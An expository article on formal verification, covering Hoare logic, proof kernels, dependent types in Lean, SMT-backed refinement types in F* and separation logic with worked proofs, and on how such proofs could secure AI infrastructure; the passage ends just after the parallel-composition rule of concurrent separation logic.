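# Proving software correct with dependent types and separation logic, and what such proofs can do for AI infrastructure

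## What it means to prove a program correct

Formal verification is the practice of proving by logic that a program satisfies a precise statement of what it should do, and having a machine check the proof. Computer scientists have pursued it since the late 1960s, mostly in research groups. Its best-known products include CompCert, a compiler that turns C programs into assembly code, and seL4, an operating-system kernel (the most privileged part of an operating system). Much of the current work uses dependent types and separation logic. Dependent types can refer to values, such as "array of length n" where an ordinary language offers only "array", so a programmer can state exact properties of code within the code itself. Separation logic extends proofs to programs that change memory and run in parallel.

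### Tests and proofs

Programmers usually gain confidence in a program by running it on some inputs and comparing the results with what they expected. In *Notes on Structured Programming*, Dijkstra (1970) showed how little this covers, using the example of a circuit in his university's computer that multiplied two 27-bit integers. At some tens of microseconds each, trying all 2^54 possible multiplications would have taken more than 10,000 years. The circuit would perform almost none of them in its working life, but nobody could know in advance which ones, so its users needed every one to be right. Dijkstra concluded that testing can show the presence of bugs but never their absence. He argued that the only hope of establishing correctness was to reason from the mechanism's structure instead of treating it as a black box.

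He also noted that if each of N components is correct with probability p, the whole system is correct with a probability of roughly p^N. A system of a thousand components, each 99.9% likely to be correct, has about a 37% chance of being correct.

Good testers choose their inputs carefully, for instance so that every line or branch of the code runs at least once, but they can still miss defects. The US National Academies' *Defense Software for a Contested Future* (2025) cites empirical studies in which deployed software often had defects in code that the tests had run, but not in a way that exposed them. Fuzzing runs a program on large numbers of generated inputs, but each run follows only one path through the code, and the number of paths grows at least exponentially with the length of the code.

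A proof avoids this by using symbols in place of particular inputs, as algebra does to show that (a + b)(a − b) = a² − b² for all numbers without testing particular values.

Every verification has four parts: a specification, which states precisely, in logic, what the program must do; the program; a proof that the program meets the specification; and a checker, which is a program that inspects the proof. A specification might require only that the program never reads past the end of an array. Functional correctness is a much stronger requirement. It means that, on every input the specification allows, the program produces the results and effects the specification describes.

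### The Hoare triple

The standard notation for such claims comes from Hoare, in *An Axiomatic Basis for Computer Programming* (1969). A Hoare triple has the form {P} C {Q}, where C is a piece of program and P and Q are assertions about the values of its variables. It means that if P holds before C runs, and C finishes, then Q holds afterwards. P is the precondition and Q the postcondition. (The 1969 paper put the braces around the program; later authors moved them.)

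Software Foundations' *Hoare Logic, Part II*, a chapter of an online textbook, has a convenient example, a program that swaps two numbers without using a third variable:

```
X := X + Y
Y := X − Y
X := X − Y
```

Starting from X = 7 and Y = 3, the program sets X to 10, then Y to 7, then X to 3. That was a test. The specification covers all cases by naming the starting values m and n:

{X = m and Y = n} *program* {X = n and Y = m}

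The proof needs one rule, the one for assignment. After `X := e`, the variable X holds whatever value the expression e had just before. So if an assertion is to be true of X afterwards, it must already be true of e, and one finds the precondition by writing e wherever the postcondition has X. This means working from the bottom of the program to the top:

1. At the end, the specification requires X = n and Y = m.
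2. Before the last line, therefore, X − Y = n and Y = m.
3. Before the middle line, X − (X − Y) = n and X − Y = m.
4. Before the first line, (X + Y) − ((X + Y) − Y) = n and (X + Y) − Y = m.

It remains to show that the precondition implies what step 4 requires. With m for X and n for Y, the two equations become n = n and m = m, which completes the proof for every pair of numbers. So much of this work suits a machine because the substitutions were mechanical and only the final implication required any mathematics.

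The algebra applied to numbers of any size, but a computer has a largest integer. Hoare distinguished three things a machine might do when a sum exceeds it: never complete the operation, return the largest integer, or wrap around to zero. He illustrated them with a toy machine whose only integers are 0, 1, 2 and 3. Suppose the swap runs on that machine with X = 3 and Y = 2. If sums wrap around, X becomes 1, Y becomes 3, X becomes 2, and the swap works. If sums stick at the maximum, X stays at 3, Y becomes 1 and X becomes 2, so the original 3 is lost. Every step in the proof is still valid, but the proof assumes that integers have no maximum.

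### Programs that never stop

Loops need one more idea. Hoare used a program that divides x by y through repeated subtraction, all the numbers being nonnegative integers:

```
r := x;  q := 0;
while y ≤ r do  (r := r − y;  q := 1 + q)
```

The proof uses a loop invariant, an assertion that is true before the loop starts and that each pass through the loop preserves. Here the invariant is x = r + y × q. Each pass subtracts y from r and adds 1 to q, which leaves the sum unchanged. When the loop ends, its condition is false, so r < y. Together, the invariant and this inequality imply that q is the quotient and r the remainder. The proof needs no precondition.

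If y = 0, the loop keeps subtracting zero and never ends. The theorem still holds, because a triple covers only runs that finish. Logicians call this partial correctness, meaning that if the program stops, the result is right. Total correctness adds that the program does stop. To prove it for the division program, we must require y > 0 and show that r shrinks on every pass and cannot fall below zero.

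Hoare was content with partial correctness, and thought it probably better to let the machine give a warning when it had to abandon a run. That is reasonable for a calculation with someone waiting for the answer, but less reasonable for an operating system routine, where a hang can take down everything that depends on it. A claim that a system is "verified" may refer only to partial correctness, which leaves open whether the system might hang.

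The 1969 rules also left out a good deal, including parallel execution and pointers (variables that hold a memory address). Hoare expected pointers to be among the omissions that would present real difficulty. Systems software relies heavily on both pointers and parallel execution, and separation logic is designed to handle them.

### Why the author of a proof need not be trustworthy

The proof for the two-line division program takes twelve lines, and Hoare called it "excessively tedious". People make mistakes in long, tedious proofs, and readers miss them. So verifiers work in a proof assistant, a program in which people or AI systems write formal proofs that a machine checks. The part that accepts or rejects a finished proof is the proof kernel, and designers try to keep it small.

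Rocq, a proof assistant called Coq until 2025, is an example of this arrangement. Its users seldom write out a proof in full. They give commands called tactics, which each automate part of the reasoning and together build a complete record of the proof, called the proof term. According to the Rocq manual, the proof kernel then checks this record from scratch. Even if a tactic is full of bugs or comes from a stranger, the kernel rejects any bad proof term it produces. This separation is called the "de Bruijn criterion".

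Isabelle, another widely used proof assistant, follows a different design called the LCF architecture, which Paulson (2022) describes in *The de Bruijn criterion vs the LCF architecture*. The rules of logic sit inside a protected data type, and the language Isabelle is written in prevents any other code from creating a theorem except by applying those rules. Isabelle therefore doesn't need to keep a record of the proof. Paulson, one of Isabelle's creators, considers such records a huge waste of space in *Why don't you use dependent types?* (2025). But he grants that a sceptic then has to trust Isabelle's proof kernel, because it produces no certificate that anyone could check independently. A certificate seems worth the space when the proof comes from someone the recipient has no reason to trust.

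In *proof-carrying code*, an older scheme, an untrusted supplier sends a program with a proof that it is safe to run, and the recipient checks the proof before running the program. *A Trustworthy Proof Checker* presents a version in which the recipient has to trust fewer than 2,700 lines of code. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, extends the reasoning to language models, arguing that a hallucinated proof does little harm because the checker rejects it and the model has to try again. Lean (2026) reports that the computer scientist Ilya Sergey has already worked this way, producing 39,000 lines of proof in 27 working days with an AI model's help.

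Kleppmann's further claim that it is virtually impossible to sneak an invalid proof past the checker is a little too strong. The manual of the proof assistant Lean puts unreviewed AI-generated proofs in the same class as malicious ones, because a Lean file can run arbitrary code while Lean processes it. A hostile file could insert a theorem that nobody proved, or change what the theorem's statement means. For high-risk cases the manual recommends a tool called comparator. The recipient writes down the theorem they want, and comparator processes the submitted proof inside a sandbox, replays it through the proof kernel outside the sandbox, and checks that the theorem proved is the one requested.

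In July 2026 the developers of Lean (2026) fixed a bug, discovered by Ramana Kumar, that let a malicious file get a proof of "False" past the proof kernel. Every other theorem follows from "False". Even Comparator did not stop it. An independent checker called nanoda had a different bug, and Kumar demonstrated a proof that exploited both at once. *Lean4Lean* (2024) had already argued that more independent checkers were needed because such bugs tend to occur where the developers never thought to test.

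Such holes are a small concern when the author is honest, since an honest author would find one only by accident and developers patch them quickly. They are a greater concern when an AI system is rewarded for any proof the kernel accepts, because it could learn to exploit them. Even so, someone who receives a proof has far less to inspect in the kernel than in the proofs it checks.

### The trusted base

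The trusted base of a verified system is everything that must be right for the proof to hold for the running system. It includes the proof checker, the specification, the model of the programming language or machine, any code that hasn't been proved correct, and the hardware. The swap program failed on the toy machine because the model was wrong.

Proof can shrink this base. With a verified compiler such as CompCert, most of the compiler no longer has to be trusted without proof. Hoare looked forward to a day when the program, compiler and hardware design would all have proofs, and only the reliability of the electronics would limit our confidence. That day is still some way off. The National Academies warn that a model may omit details such as timing, or misdescribe the hardware and older software around the verified part.

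The specification is the one thing that always has to be trusted, however much is proved, because a proof can only compare a program with some statement of what it should do. The National Academies give the example of a service specified to take a line of input, parse it and execute it. A proof could establish beyond doubt that the service does this, but a person has to read the specification to notice that the service perhaps shouldn't execute whatever a stranger sends. Kleppmann expects getting the specification right to become the main difficulty once machines write the proofs.

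### Proof assistants with and without dependent types

Rocq, Lean, F* and Agda all have dependent types. Isabelle/HOL, the most common form of Isabelle, does not. Unruh (2024) notes this in *With-Type* and builds a partial substitute. The seL4 proof is in Isabelle/HOL, so programs can be verified without dependent types. Whether dependent types are the best approach depends on the program.

### What there is to prove in an AI system

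AI infrastructure is the conventional software and hardware that trains, stores, serves and isolates AI models. Roughly, from the bottom up, it consists of:

- processors, graphics processors (GPUs) and their firmware;
- operating-system kernels and hypervisors, which divide one physical machine among several users and keep them apart;
- cryptography and access control, which keep data and model weights from people who should not have them;
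- databases, schedulers and the servers that carry requests to a model and answers back;
- numerical code, including compilers and GPU kernels, the functions that run in parallel on a graphics processor to do such things as multiply matrices.

OpenAI describes crashes in Rockset, a part of ChatGPT's data infrastructure that supports searching over conversations. A normal C++ function seemed to finish and then returned to an address that held no code. It should have returned control to its caller. That requirement is easy to state, so a specification can cover this kind of fault, whatever its cause.

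The learned component is the trained network itself. Training produces the numerical weights that determine its behaviour, and no programmer wrote down the steps by which it answers a question. A proof about the numerical code could establish that the computer multiplies those weights correctly, but it would not rule out dangerous advice that results from the weights themselves.

That leaves the infrastructure as the natural place to start, though there is little to build on yet. Galois' *Formal Verification Has Become Essential*, an essay from a company that specialises in this work, concedes that verified systems are still rare, expensive and mostly isolated from one another, and calls for guarantees that span the whole stack. A verified hypervisor running on faulty firmware gives less protection than its theorem implies. The question for AI infrastructure is therefore which of these layers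 people or machines can prove correct, to what standard, and at what cost.

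## Dependent types: how a type checker checks a proof

Most programmers already use a type checker, which checks small proofs about their code. In a typed language, every value has a type, such as number or text, and the type checker inspects the program before it runs. If a function expects a number and the program passes it the text "twelve", the type checker rejects the program. It works out the type of each expression from the program's text, without trying any inputs. When it accepts a program, it has proved a weak theorem, that no input can cause this kind of mistake.

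The theorem rules out more when the types can express more. In Lean, the type `List String` covers lists of text of every length, so the type alone cannot exclude a request for the fourth element of a three-element list. A dependent type can exclude it because the type refers to a value, in this case the list's length.

### A list with its length in its type

Lean's programming textbook defines lists of known length, which it calls vectors, more or less like this:

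```
inductive Vect (α : Type) : Nat → Type where
  | nil  : Vect α 0
  | cons : α → Vect α n → Vect α (n + 1)
```

In the first line, `α` is the type of the elements, and `Nat → Type` means that `Vect α` becomes a type only when given a natural number, the length. So `Vect String 3` and `Vect String 4` are different types. The other two lines give the only ways to build a vector. `nil` is the empty vector, of length 0. `cons` adds an element to the front of a vector of length n, which makes a vector of length n + 1. Computer scientists call `Vect` an indexed type, or indexed family, and the length is its index.

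If a program supplies `nil`, which has length 0, where it needs a `Vect String 3`, Lean reports a type mismatch, just as it would if the program supplied text where it needed a number.

The textbook shows what kind of error this catches with `replicate`, a function that should return n copies of a value. If the programmer mistakenly adds the value twice at each step, Lean still accepts the function when it returns an ordinary list, and the result has 2n copies. Lean rejects the same mistake before the program runs if the function returns a vector, because the return type requires length n.

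### Looking up an element safely

Safe lookup needs a second indexed type, for positions within a vector. `Index n` has exactly n values, standing for the positions 0 to n − 1. (Lean's reference manual defines the same type under the name `Fin'`.)

```
inductive Index : Nat → Type where
  | zero : Index (n + 1)
  | succ : Index n → Index (n + 1)

def get : Vect α n → Index n → α
  | .cons x _,  .zero   => x
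  | .cons _ xs, .succ i => get xs i
```

`zero` is the first position in any vector that has at least one element, and `succ` moves one place along. The type of `get` uses the same n for the vector's length and the position, so the position must exist in the vector. The first case of `get` returns the front element x when the position is zero. The second drops the front element and looks up position i in the rest, xs.

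Lean accepts the definition without a case for the empty vector. If the vector is `nil`, then n is 0 and the position must have type `Index 0`. Both ways of building an index give a type of the form `Index (n + 1)`, so no value of type `Index 0` exists.

Now suppose that v has three elements and a program asks for a fourth, by writing `get v (.succ (.succ (.succ .zero)))`. The type checker proceeds from the outside in:

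1. v has length 3, so `get` needs an `Index 3`.
2. The outermost `succ` gives an `Index 3` only if it contains an `Index 2`.
3. By the same rule, the next `succ` must contain an `Index 1`, and the innermost an `Index 0`.
4. The innermost value is `zero`, whose type is `Index (n + 1)`. No natural number n makes n + 1 equal to 0, so the program has a type error.

Nobody wants to count in `succ`s, and everyday Lean code has the usual notation `xs[3]`. When it meets this, Lean tries to prove that 3 is less than the length of xs, and refuses to compile the program if it can't. Sometimes the length isn't known, as in a function that returns the third element of whatever list it receives. The function can then demand evidence from its caller:

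```
def third (xs : List α) (ok : xs.length > 2) : α := xs[2]
```

The argument `ok` is a proof that the list has more than two elements. Lean checks this proof at compile time, so the lookup needs no bounds check at run time. The same is true for arrays. A programmer who cannot prove the bound can write `xs[2]?`, which returns `none` if the position doesn't exist, or `xs[2]!`, which crashes the program in that case.

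### Appending, and arithmetic that gets stuck

Appending a vector of length k to one of length n should give a vector of length n + k. Lean's textbook begins with its own version of addition, for a reason that will become clear:

```
def plusL : Nat → Nat → Nat
  | 0,     k => k
  | n + 1, k => plusL n k + 1

def append : Vect α n → Vect α k → Vect α (plusL n k)
  | .nil,       ys => ys
  | .cons x xs, ys => .cons x (append xs ys)
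```

`append` returns `ys` if the first vector is empty. Otherwise it appends `ys` to the rest of the first vector and puts the first element, `x`, back on the front. Lean has to check that each case returns a vector of the length given in the type.

In the first case n is 0, so the result must have length `plusL 0 k`. Lean runs the first line of `plusL`, gets k, and checks that ys has length k. In the second case n is m + 1, where m is the length of xs. The result must have length `plusL (m + 1) k`, which the second line of `plusL` turns into `plusL m k + 1`. The recursive call gives a vector of length `plusL m k` and `cons` adds one, so the lengths agree. If the programmer forgot x and returned only `append xs ys`, the result would be one element short and Lean would reject it.

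So the type checker has to compute. Two expressions are definitionally equal if it can show that they are the same by running definitions, and it checks this kind of equality automatically.

The same program fails with Lean's ordinary addition, which recurses on its second argument instead of its first. The first case now needs a vector of length 0 + k, which Lean cannot simplify because k may or may not be zero. The programmer has to prove that 0 + k = k by induction on k. The second case needs a proof that (m + 1) + k = (m + k) + 1. Once the programmer has written both proofs, Lean can use them to rewrite the type, and `append` type-checks.

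Programming with dependent types is awkward here because a function's definition becomes part of every type that mentions it. Replacing one version of addition with the other breaks `append`, even though both always give the same answers. The textbook adds that comparing types can be slow when it involves running complicated functions, and the resulting error messages can be hard to follow.

### Dependent functions and dependent pairs

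The type of `replicate`, with its first argument named, is `(n : Nat) → α → Vect α n`. This is a dependent function type because the type of the result depends on the value of the first argument. When that argument is 3, the function returns a vector of length 3. The general form is `(x : A) → B x`, which logicians write Π x : A. B(x), where B gives a type for each x in A. An ordinary function type is the special case in which B x is the same type for every x.

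A dependent pair has the type `(x : A) × B x`, also written Σ x : A. B(x). It consists of a value x and a second value whose type depends on x. A program that reads lines from a file might return `(n : Nat) × Vect String n`, a number together with a vector of that length, because the number of lines isn't known until the program runs.

The symbols Π and Σ, the usual signs for a product and a sum, come from counting. Suppose A has two values, and B assigns a type with 3 values to the first and a type with 5 values to the second. A dependent function picks one value from each type, so there are 3 × 5 = 15 functions. A dependent pair picks one of the two types and then a value from it, so there are 3 + 5 = 8 pairs.

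### Propositions as types

The argument `ok` in `third` had the type `xs.length > 2`, which is a proposition. In Lean, propositions are types, and the values of such a type are the proofs of the proposition. A false proposition is a type with no values. Each logical connective then corresponds to a way of building types:

| Proposition | What a proof of it is |
|---|---|
| A and B | a pair, of a proof of A and a proof of B |
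| A or B | a proof of one of them, with a label for which |
| A implies B | a function that turns any proof of A into a proof of B |
| False | nothing, since this type has no values |
| not A | a function that turns any proof of A into a proof of False |
| for all x, P(x) | a dependent function from each x to a proof of P(x) |
| for some x, P(x) | a dependent pair of an x and a proof of P(x) |

The fact that held up `append`, that 0 + k = k for all k, makes a good example. Its proof is a function that takes any k and returns a proof for that k:

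```
theorem zero_plus : (k : Nat) → 0 + k = k
  | 0     => rfl
  | k + 1 => congrArg (· + 1) (zero_plus k)
```

This is a proof by induction, written as a recursive function. When k is 0, both sides compute to 0, so `rfl`, the proof that a thing equals itself, proves this case. For k + 1, the function calls itself to get a proof that 0 + k = k, and `congrArg` adds one to both sides.

This idea is called the Curry–Howard correspondence, after the logicians Haskell Curry and William Howard. Pfenning (2009), in *Lecture Notes on Proofs as Programs*, credits Per Martin-Löf with developing it into a more expressive system, type theory. Lean uses a later related system, the Calculus of Constructions.

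One can accept this without believing that propositions really are types. Lean's introduction to theorem proving allows the reader to regard the correspondence as a coding trick, in which each proposition is assigned a type that has a value exactly when the proposition is true. Lean treats any two proofs of the same proposition as equal, so a program's results can't depend on which proof it received.

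### The type of a sorting function

With propositions available as types, a programmer can put a full specification into a function's type. For sorting a list of numbers it might be:

```
def sort (xs : List Nat) :
    { ys : List Nat // Sorted ys ∧ Perm ys xs }
```

The braces describe the lists ys that meet two conditions. `Sorted ys` means that no element is larger than the one after it. `Perm ys xs` means that ys is a permutation of xs, with the same elements, each the same number of times, in any order. The function has to return both a list and a proof that the list meets the two conditions. A type narrowed by conditions like these is called a refinement type.

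Both clauses are necessary, because if either were missing or too weak, a useless program could have a valid proof. Without `Perm`, a function that always returns the empty list would pass, because the empty list is sorted. Without `Sorted`, a function that returns its input unchanged would pass. A clause that is slightly too weak is harder to notice than a missing one. If the second clause required only that the lists have the same length, a function could turn [3, 1, 3] into [0, 0, 0]. If it required only that every number in one list also occur in the other, the function could return [1, 3].

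A programmer can also give the function an ordinary type and prove the specification as a separate theorem. *CSLib* (Barrett, Chaudhuri and colleagues, 2026), a proposal for a library of verified computer science in Lean, does this for merge sort, with the same two clauses. That theorem doesn't cover speed, so a second one bounds the number of comparisons by n times the logarithm of n to base 2, rounded up. The programmer has to mark each comparison by hand for it to be counted, and Barrett and colleagues acknowledge that someone could get these marks wrong. The proved bound would then apply to the number of marks counted, which could differ from the number of comparisons.

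### What the proof kernel does, and what tactics do

If propositions are types, then checking a proof is type checking. Lean's kernel receives a proposition and a proof term, infers the term's type, and checks that it matches the proposition.

Much of proof checking consists of applying one rule. If f has the type `(x : A) → B x` and a has the type A, then f applied to a has the type `B a`. For instance, `zero_plus` has the type `(k : Nat) → 0 + k = k` and 5 is a natural number, so `zero_plus 5` is a proof that 0 + 5 = 5. The kernel never has to find a proof, because it is given the term and applies this rule and a modest number of others to every part of it, comparing types by definitional equality, as in `append`.

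The author has to find the proof, usually with tactics. A tactic works on a goal, which is a proposition still to prove, together with the available assumptions. To prove 0 + k = k, the author might use the tactic `induction`, which replaces the goal with two others. One is 0 + 0 = 0. The other is 0 + (k + 1) = k + 1, with 0 + k = k as an assumption. The author then applies more tactics until no goals remain. Alternatively, the author can use `simp`, which proves 0 + k = k in one step by simplifying it with facts from Lean's library. The notation `xs[3]` runs a tactic in the background to prove that the index is within bounds, so programmers seldom have to write such proofs themselves.

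### Why a proof has to terminate

Hoare's rules tolerate programs that never stop, but a type theory used as a logic cannot. Consider this attempt at a theorem:

```
theorem oops : 1 = 0 := oops
```

The theorem `oops`, which states that 1 = 0, uses itself as its proof. If Lean allowed unrestricted recursion, this definition would type-check, because the `oops` on the right-hand side is assumed to have the type 1 = 0. An ordinary program defined this way would hang when run. But the kernel accepts a proof because of its type, without running it, so the loop would go unnoticed and 1 = 0 would be a theorem.

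The circle can be less obvious. Lean's developers give the example of a function that tries 0, 1, 2 and so on until a test succeeds, then returns what it found. This is an ordinary program that can find the square root of 121. But with a test that always fails, it can be declared to return a value of any type, including the type 1 = 0.

Lean requires evidence that each recursive function terminates. In the simplest case, each recursive call works on a smaller piece of the input, as when `append` moves from `cons x xs` to `xs`. Otherwise the programmer or Lean has to find a quantity that shrinks with every call, like the remainder in Hoare's division program. No algorithm can recognise every function that terminates, so Lean rejects some that do. For example, the Lean manual has a countdown function that Lean rejects when it tests whether `n` is zero with `==`, which gives a Boolean. Lean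 accepts the function when the test uses `=`, which gives a proposition that Lean's automation can use.

A programmer who only wants to run a function can mark it `partial`. Lean then hides the function's definition from the kernel, so almost nothing can be proved about its behaviour. Lean also requires the function's result type to have at least one value, so that the function can't be used to "prove" something false.

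None of this prevents an author from assuming a falsehood outright. Lean lets anyone declare an axiom, even "False", and accepts whatever follows from it, so the recipient of a proof should check which axioms it uses.

### Refinement types and SMT solvers

Supplying a proof with every refined value can be tiresome, and most of the proofs are dull facts about arithmetic. The language F* delegates them. A lookup function in F* might have this type:

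```
val nth : #a:Type -> xs:list a -> i:nat{i < length xs} -> a
```

The position i is a natural number, refined by the condition that it is less than the length of xs. The caller passes only the number. F* collects the conditions the program must satisfy and sends them to Z3, an SMT solver. An SMT solver is a program that automatically decides many logical formulas about things like numbers and arrays.

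Suppose the program tests that i + 1 < length xs and then calls `nth xs i`. F* must establish that i < length xs, so it uses Z3 to search for a counterexample, which would be integers i and L such that i + 1 < L but i ≥ L. Z3 determines that none exist, and F* accepts the call. F* also has indexed types. *Length-indexed Lists*, part of the F* tutorial, defines separate types for lists of even and odd length. The solver can easily prove that 0 + k = k, so an F* programmer can write `append` with ordinary addition and avoid the problem that needed two proofs in Lean.

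This convenience requires trusting more code. When Z3 reports that no counterexample exists, F* accepts the result without checking it. There is no complete proof term for a small proof kernel to check, so the trusted base includes both Z3, which is large and intricate, and the code that translates F* conditions into Z3's language.

Proofs can also be unstable. Many conditions involve "for all", and no algorithm can decide every such condition, so the solver searches by rules of thumb under a time limit. A small edit can change the search, and a proof that used to work may fail even though the theorem is still true. In a June 2026 talk, Lean's developers said that Z3 had caught thousands of defects at Microsoft but its proofs were too brittle for verifying whole programs. Leonardo de Moura, who created Z3, started Lean in 2013 to combine automatic and interactive proof.

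Lean now addresses this with a tactic called `grind`, which borrows techniques from SMT solvers but produces a proof term that the kernel checks, so it adds nothing to the trusted base. The old objection to this approach was that it was too slow. The same talk included preliminary results for Velvet, a verifier built in Lean and modelled on Dafny, a language that relies on an SMT solver. Velvet had been about three times slower than Dafny, but after a redesign it was faster on 24 of 27 benchmarks. These figures come from Lean's proponents and cover a small set of programs, but they suggest that checkable proofs need not be much slower.

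### Values that never change

All the functions in these examples are pure, meaning that their results depend only on their arguments and they change nothing else. `append` returns a new vector and leaves the two old ones unchanged. In Lean's logic, even updating an array yields a new array, although the running program overwrites the old one if nothing else refers to it.

Most systems code is different because it changes memory in place. Suppose a C program has an array of length 4 and a proof that 3 < 4, so it may read position 3. Another part of the program, with a pointer to the same array, then shrinks it to two elements. 3 < 4 is still true, but the program now reads past the end of the array. The type `Vect String 4` describes a value, but does not by itself determine which code may change the memory where that value is stored.

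## Separation logic: proofs about memory and threads

A program that changes memory in place can make a fact about one variable false while appearing to change only another. The notation `[x]` means the contents of the memory cell at address x. Suppose the cell at address y contains 3 and the program runs `[x] := 4`. The cell at y still contains 3 if x and y are different addresses, but it now contains 4 if they are the same. Programmers call the second case aliasing, because x and y are two names for one cell.

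Hoare's logic gives the wrong answer here because of its rule of constancy, which large proofs depend on. If someone has proved {P} C {Q}, and R is an assertion about variables that C doesn't change, the rule gives {P and R} C {Q and R}. This lets people prove a small piece of code by itself and add the surrounding facts later. *Separation Logic* (Reynolds, 2002) shows how the rule fails. The command `[x] := 4` changes the cell at address x but doesn't change any variable. The rule therefore lets us conclude that the cell at y still contains 3, which is false if x = y.

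Adding x ≠ y to the precondition fixes this, but ten pointers need 45 such conditions, one for each pair. Linked data structures are worse because their number of cells isn't known until the program runs. Reynolds's main example is a program that reverses a linked list in place. The program works with two lists at a time, so in ordinary Hoare logic its loop invariant has to include the condition that no cell is reachable from both. If a third list elsewhere in memory must stay unchanged, the invariant also has to require that this list shares no cells with the other two, even though the loop never accesses it.

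### Assertions about part of memory

Reynolds, Peter O'Hearn and others developed separation logic around 2000. (Reynolds's own first version, in 1999, had flaws.) Its assertions describe a piece of the heap, which is the collection of memory cells that the program has allocated and not yet freed. There are four new forms:

- emp means that the piece contains no cells.
- x ↦ v, read "x points to v", means that it consists of exactly one cell, at address x, with contents v. If the contents don't matter, one writes x ↦ –.
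- P * Q, the separating conjunction, means that one can divide the piece into two parts with no cell in common, so that P holds of one part and Q of the other.
- P −* Q, the separating implication or "magic wand", means that if one adds any separate piece of which P holds, Q holds of the result.

The assertion x ↦ 1 * y ↦ 2 implies that x ≠ y, because two disjoint parts of the heap cannot both contain the cell at the same address. The assertion x ↦ 1 * x ↦ 1 is also false of every heap for this reason. So P does not in general imply P * P, whereas in ordinary logic P always implies P ∧ P. An assertion such as x ↦ 1 is more like a possession than a fact, so researchers say that code with x ↦ v in its precondition owns the cell at x.

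Triples also become stricter. {P} C {Q} now requires that C, when it starts in a state satisfying P, never reads, writes or frees a cell that isn't allocated. A piece of code can therefore only touch cells that its precondition provides or that it allocates itself. The rules for writing, freeing and allocating a cell mention that cell and nothing else:

```
{x ↦ –}   [x] := v       {x ↦ v}
{x ↦ –}   dispose x      {emp}
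{emp}     x := cons(v)   {x ↦ v}     (where v does not mention x)
```

The magic wand is useful for working backwards, as in the proof of the swap program. For Q to hold after `[x] := v`, it is enough that x ↦ – * (x ↦ v −* Q) holds before. This means that the code owns the cell at x, and that Q would hold if a cell at x containing v were added to the rest of its memory.

### The frame rule

O'Hearn's replacement for the rule of constancy is the frame rule:

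```
If     {P} C {Q}
then   {P * R} C {Q * R},
provided that C assigns to no variable that R mentions.
```

To repair the example, start from {x ↦ –} [x] := 4 {x ↦ 4} and let R be y ↦ 3. The frame rule gives

{x ↦ – * y ↦ 3} [x] := 4 {x ↦ 4 * y ↦ 3}

which is true. Its precondition can't hold when x = y, so the bad case never arises, and nobody had to write down x ≠ y.

The side condition is needed because variables are stored outside the heap. The triple {emp} y := 7 {emp} is true. Without the side condition, one could add y ↦ 3 to both sides and derive {y ↦ 3} y := 7 {y ↦ 3}. This triple is false because y holds the address 7 after the assignment, and the cell containing 3 is usually at a different address.

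The frame rule is sound because triples exclude memory faults. Suppose the heap has two parts, with P true of one and R true of the other. The triple for C guarantees that C would run without a fault if the P part were the whole heap. C therefore never touches an existing cell outside that part, so it leaves the R part unchanged. If a triple could hold even when its command faults, as Hoare's triples can when the command loops forever, the frame rule would be unsound. The triple {emp} [x] := 4 {emp} would be true, because the command faults on an empty heap and never finishes. The frame rule would then let us add x ↦ 3 to both sides and "prove" that writing 4 into a cell leaves 3 in it.

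In *Local Reasoning about Shared Mutable Data Structure* (2001), O'Hearn, Reynolds and Yang call this style of proof local reasoning, because a specification can describe just the memory that the code uses. Yang also showed that the frame rule is as strong as it could be. Given only a single triple about C, the frame rule and three routine rules are enough to derive every other triple that follows from it.

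### Reversing a list in place

A linked list stores each element in a pair of neighbouring cells, one for the element and one for the address of the next pair. Write i ↦ a, j as short for i ↦ a * i + 1 ↦ j. The assertion `list α i` means that i is the start of a linked list containing the sequence α. Its definition is recursive, like that of `Vect`:

```
list ε i        =   emp  and  i = nil
list (a·α) i    =   for some j,   i ↦ a, j  *  list α j
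```

Here ε is the empty sequence, a·α is the sequence with a in front of α, and nil is a value that is not an address. The * in the second line makes each pair of cells separate from the rest of the list, so the list cannot loop back on itself.

The program that reverses the list at i and leaves the result at j is

```
j := nil;
while i ≠ nil do
  k := [i + 1];     // remember where the rest of the list starts
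  [i + 1] := j;     // link the front pair to the reversed part
  j := i;           // the reversed part now starts at that pair
  i := k            // continue with the rest
```

Each pass moves the front pair of the list at i to the front of the list at j. If the list starts as 1, 2, 3, then after one pass i holds 2, 3 and j holds 1. After two passes i holds 3 and j holds 2, 1.

Let α₀ be the original sequence, and write rev for the reverse of a sequence. The loop invariant is that, for some α and β,

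(list α i * list β j) and rev(α₀) = rev(α)·β

After one pass in the example, rev(α) is 3, 2 and β is 1, which together make 3, 2, 1. Before the loop, α is α₀ and β is empty, so the invariant holds. When the loop ends, i is nil, so α is empty and β must be rev(α₀), as the specification requires.

It remains to show that each pass preserves the invariant. Since i ≠ nil, the sequence at i has a first element, so it is a·α for some a and a shorter α. Unfolding the definition exposes the two cells that hold it:

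```
{for some m,  i ↦ a, m  *  list α m  *  list β j}
k := [i + 1];
{i ↦ a, k  *  list α k  *  list β j}
[i + 1] := j;
{i ↦ a, j  *  list α k  *  list β j}
{list α k  *  list (a·β) i}
j := i;  i := k
{list α i  *  list (a·β) j}
```

The first command reads the address of the next pair into k. Only the second command changes the heap. It overwrites the single cell at i + 1, and by the frame rule, both lists stay unchanged. The pair at i now points to the list at j, so by the definition of `list` they form the list a·β starting at i. The last two assignments only rename the starting points. The equation about sequences still holds because rev(a·α)·β and rev(α)·(a·β) are the same sequence.

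The * in the invariant means that the two lists share no cells, so the proof needs no separate argument that the write leaves the list at j intact. The third list, at x, needed extra conditions in Hoare's logic, but here it requires only one application of the frame rule. *An Introduction to Separation Logic*, a set of lecture slides, goes directly from {list α i} REV {list rev(α) j}, where REV is the whole program, to {list α i * list γ x} REV {list rev(α) j * list γ x}.

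Proofs become harder when a data structure is supposed to share memory. Reynolds gives the example of a procedure that copies a tree whose branches may overlap. The natural specification, that the original still represents the same tree afterwards and the copy is separate, would let the procedure rearrange the original's inner cells. A pointer from another branch into one of those cells could then lead to the wrong subtree. The frame rule can't exclude this, because the branches are not separate. Reynolds therefore strengthens the specification to require that every property of the original heap survives the copying, and that the copy is separate from that heap.

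### Threads with separate memory

A thread is a sequence of instructions that runs at the same time as others and can use the same memory. Threads make aliasing much more dangerous, because one thread can change a cell between any two steps of another. Brookes and O'Hearn recall in *Concurrent Separation Logic* (2016) that researchers had proved few realistic concurrent programs correct before their work. Methods from the 1970s and 1980s could handle this interference, but the proofs became long, and people had to treat memory as one global array when programs used pointers.

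The central rule of concurrent separation logic deals with threads that don't interfere:

```
If     {P₁} C₁ {Q₁}   and   {P₂} C₂ {Q₂}
then   {P₁ * P₂}  C₁ ∥ C₂  {Q₁ * Q₂}
```

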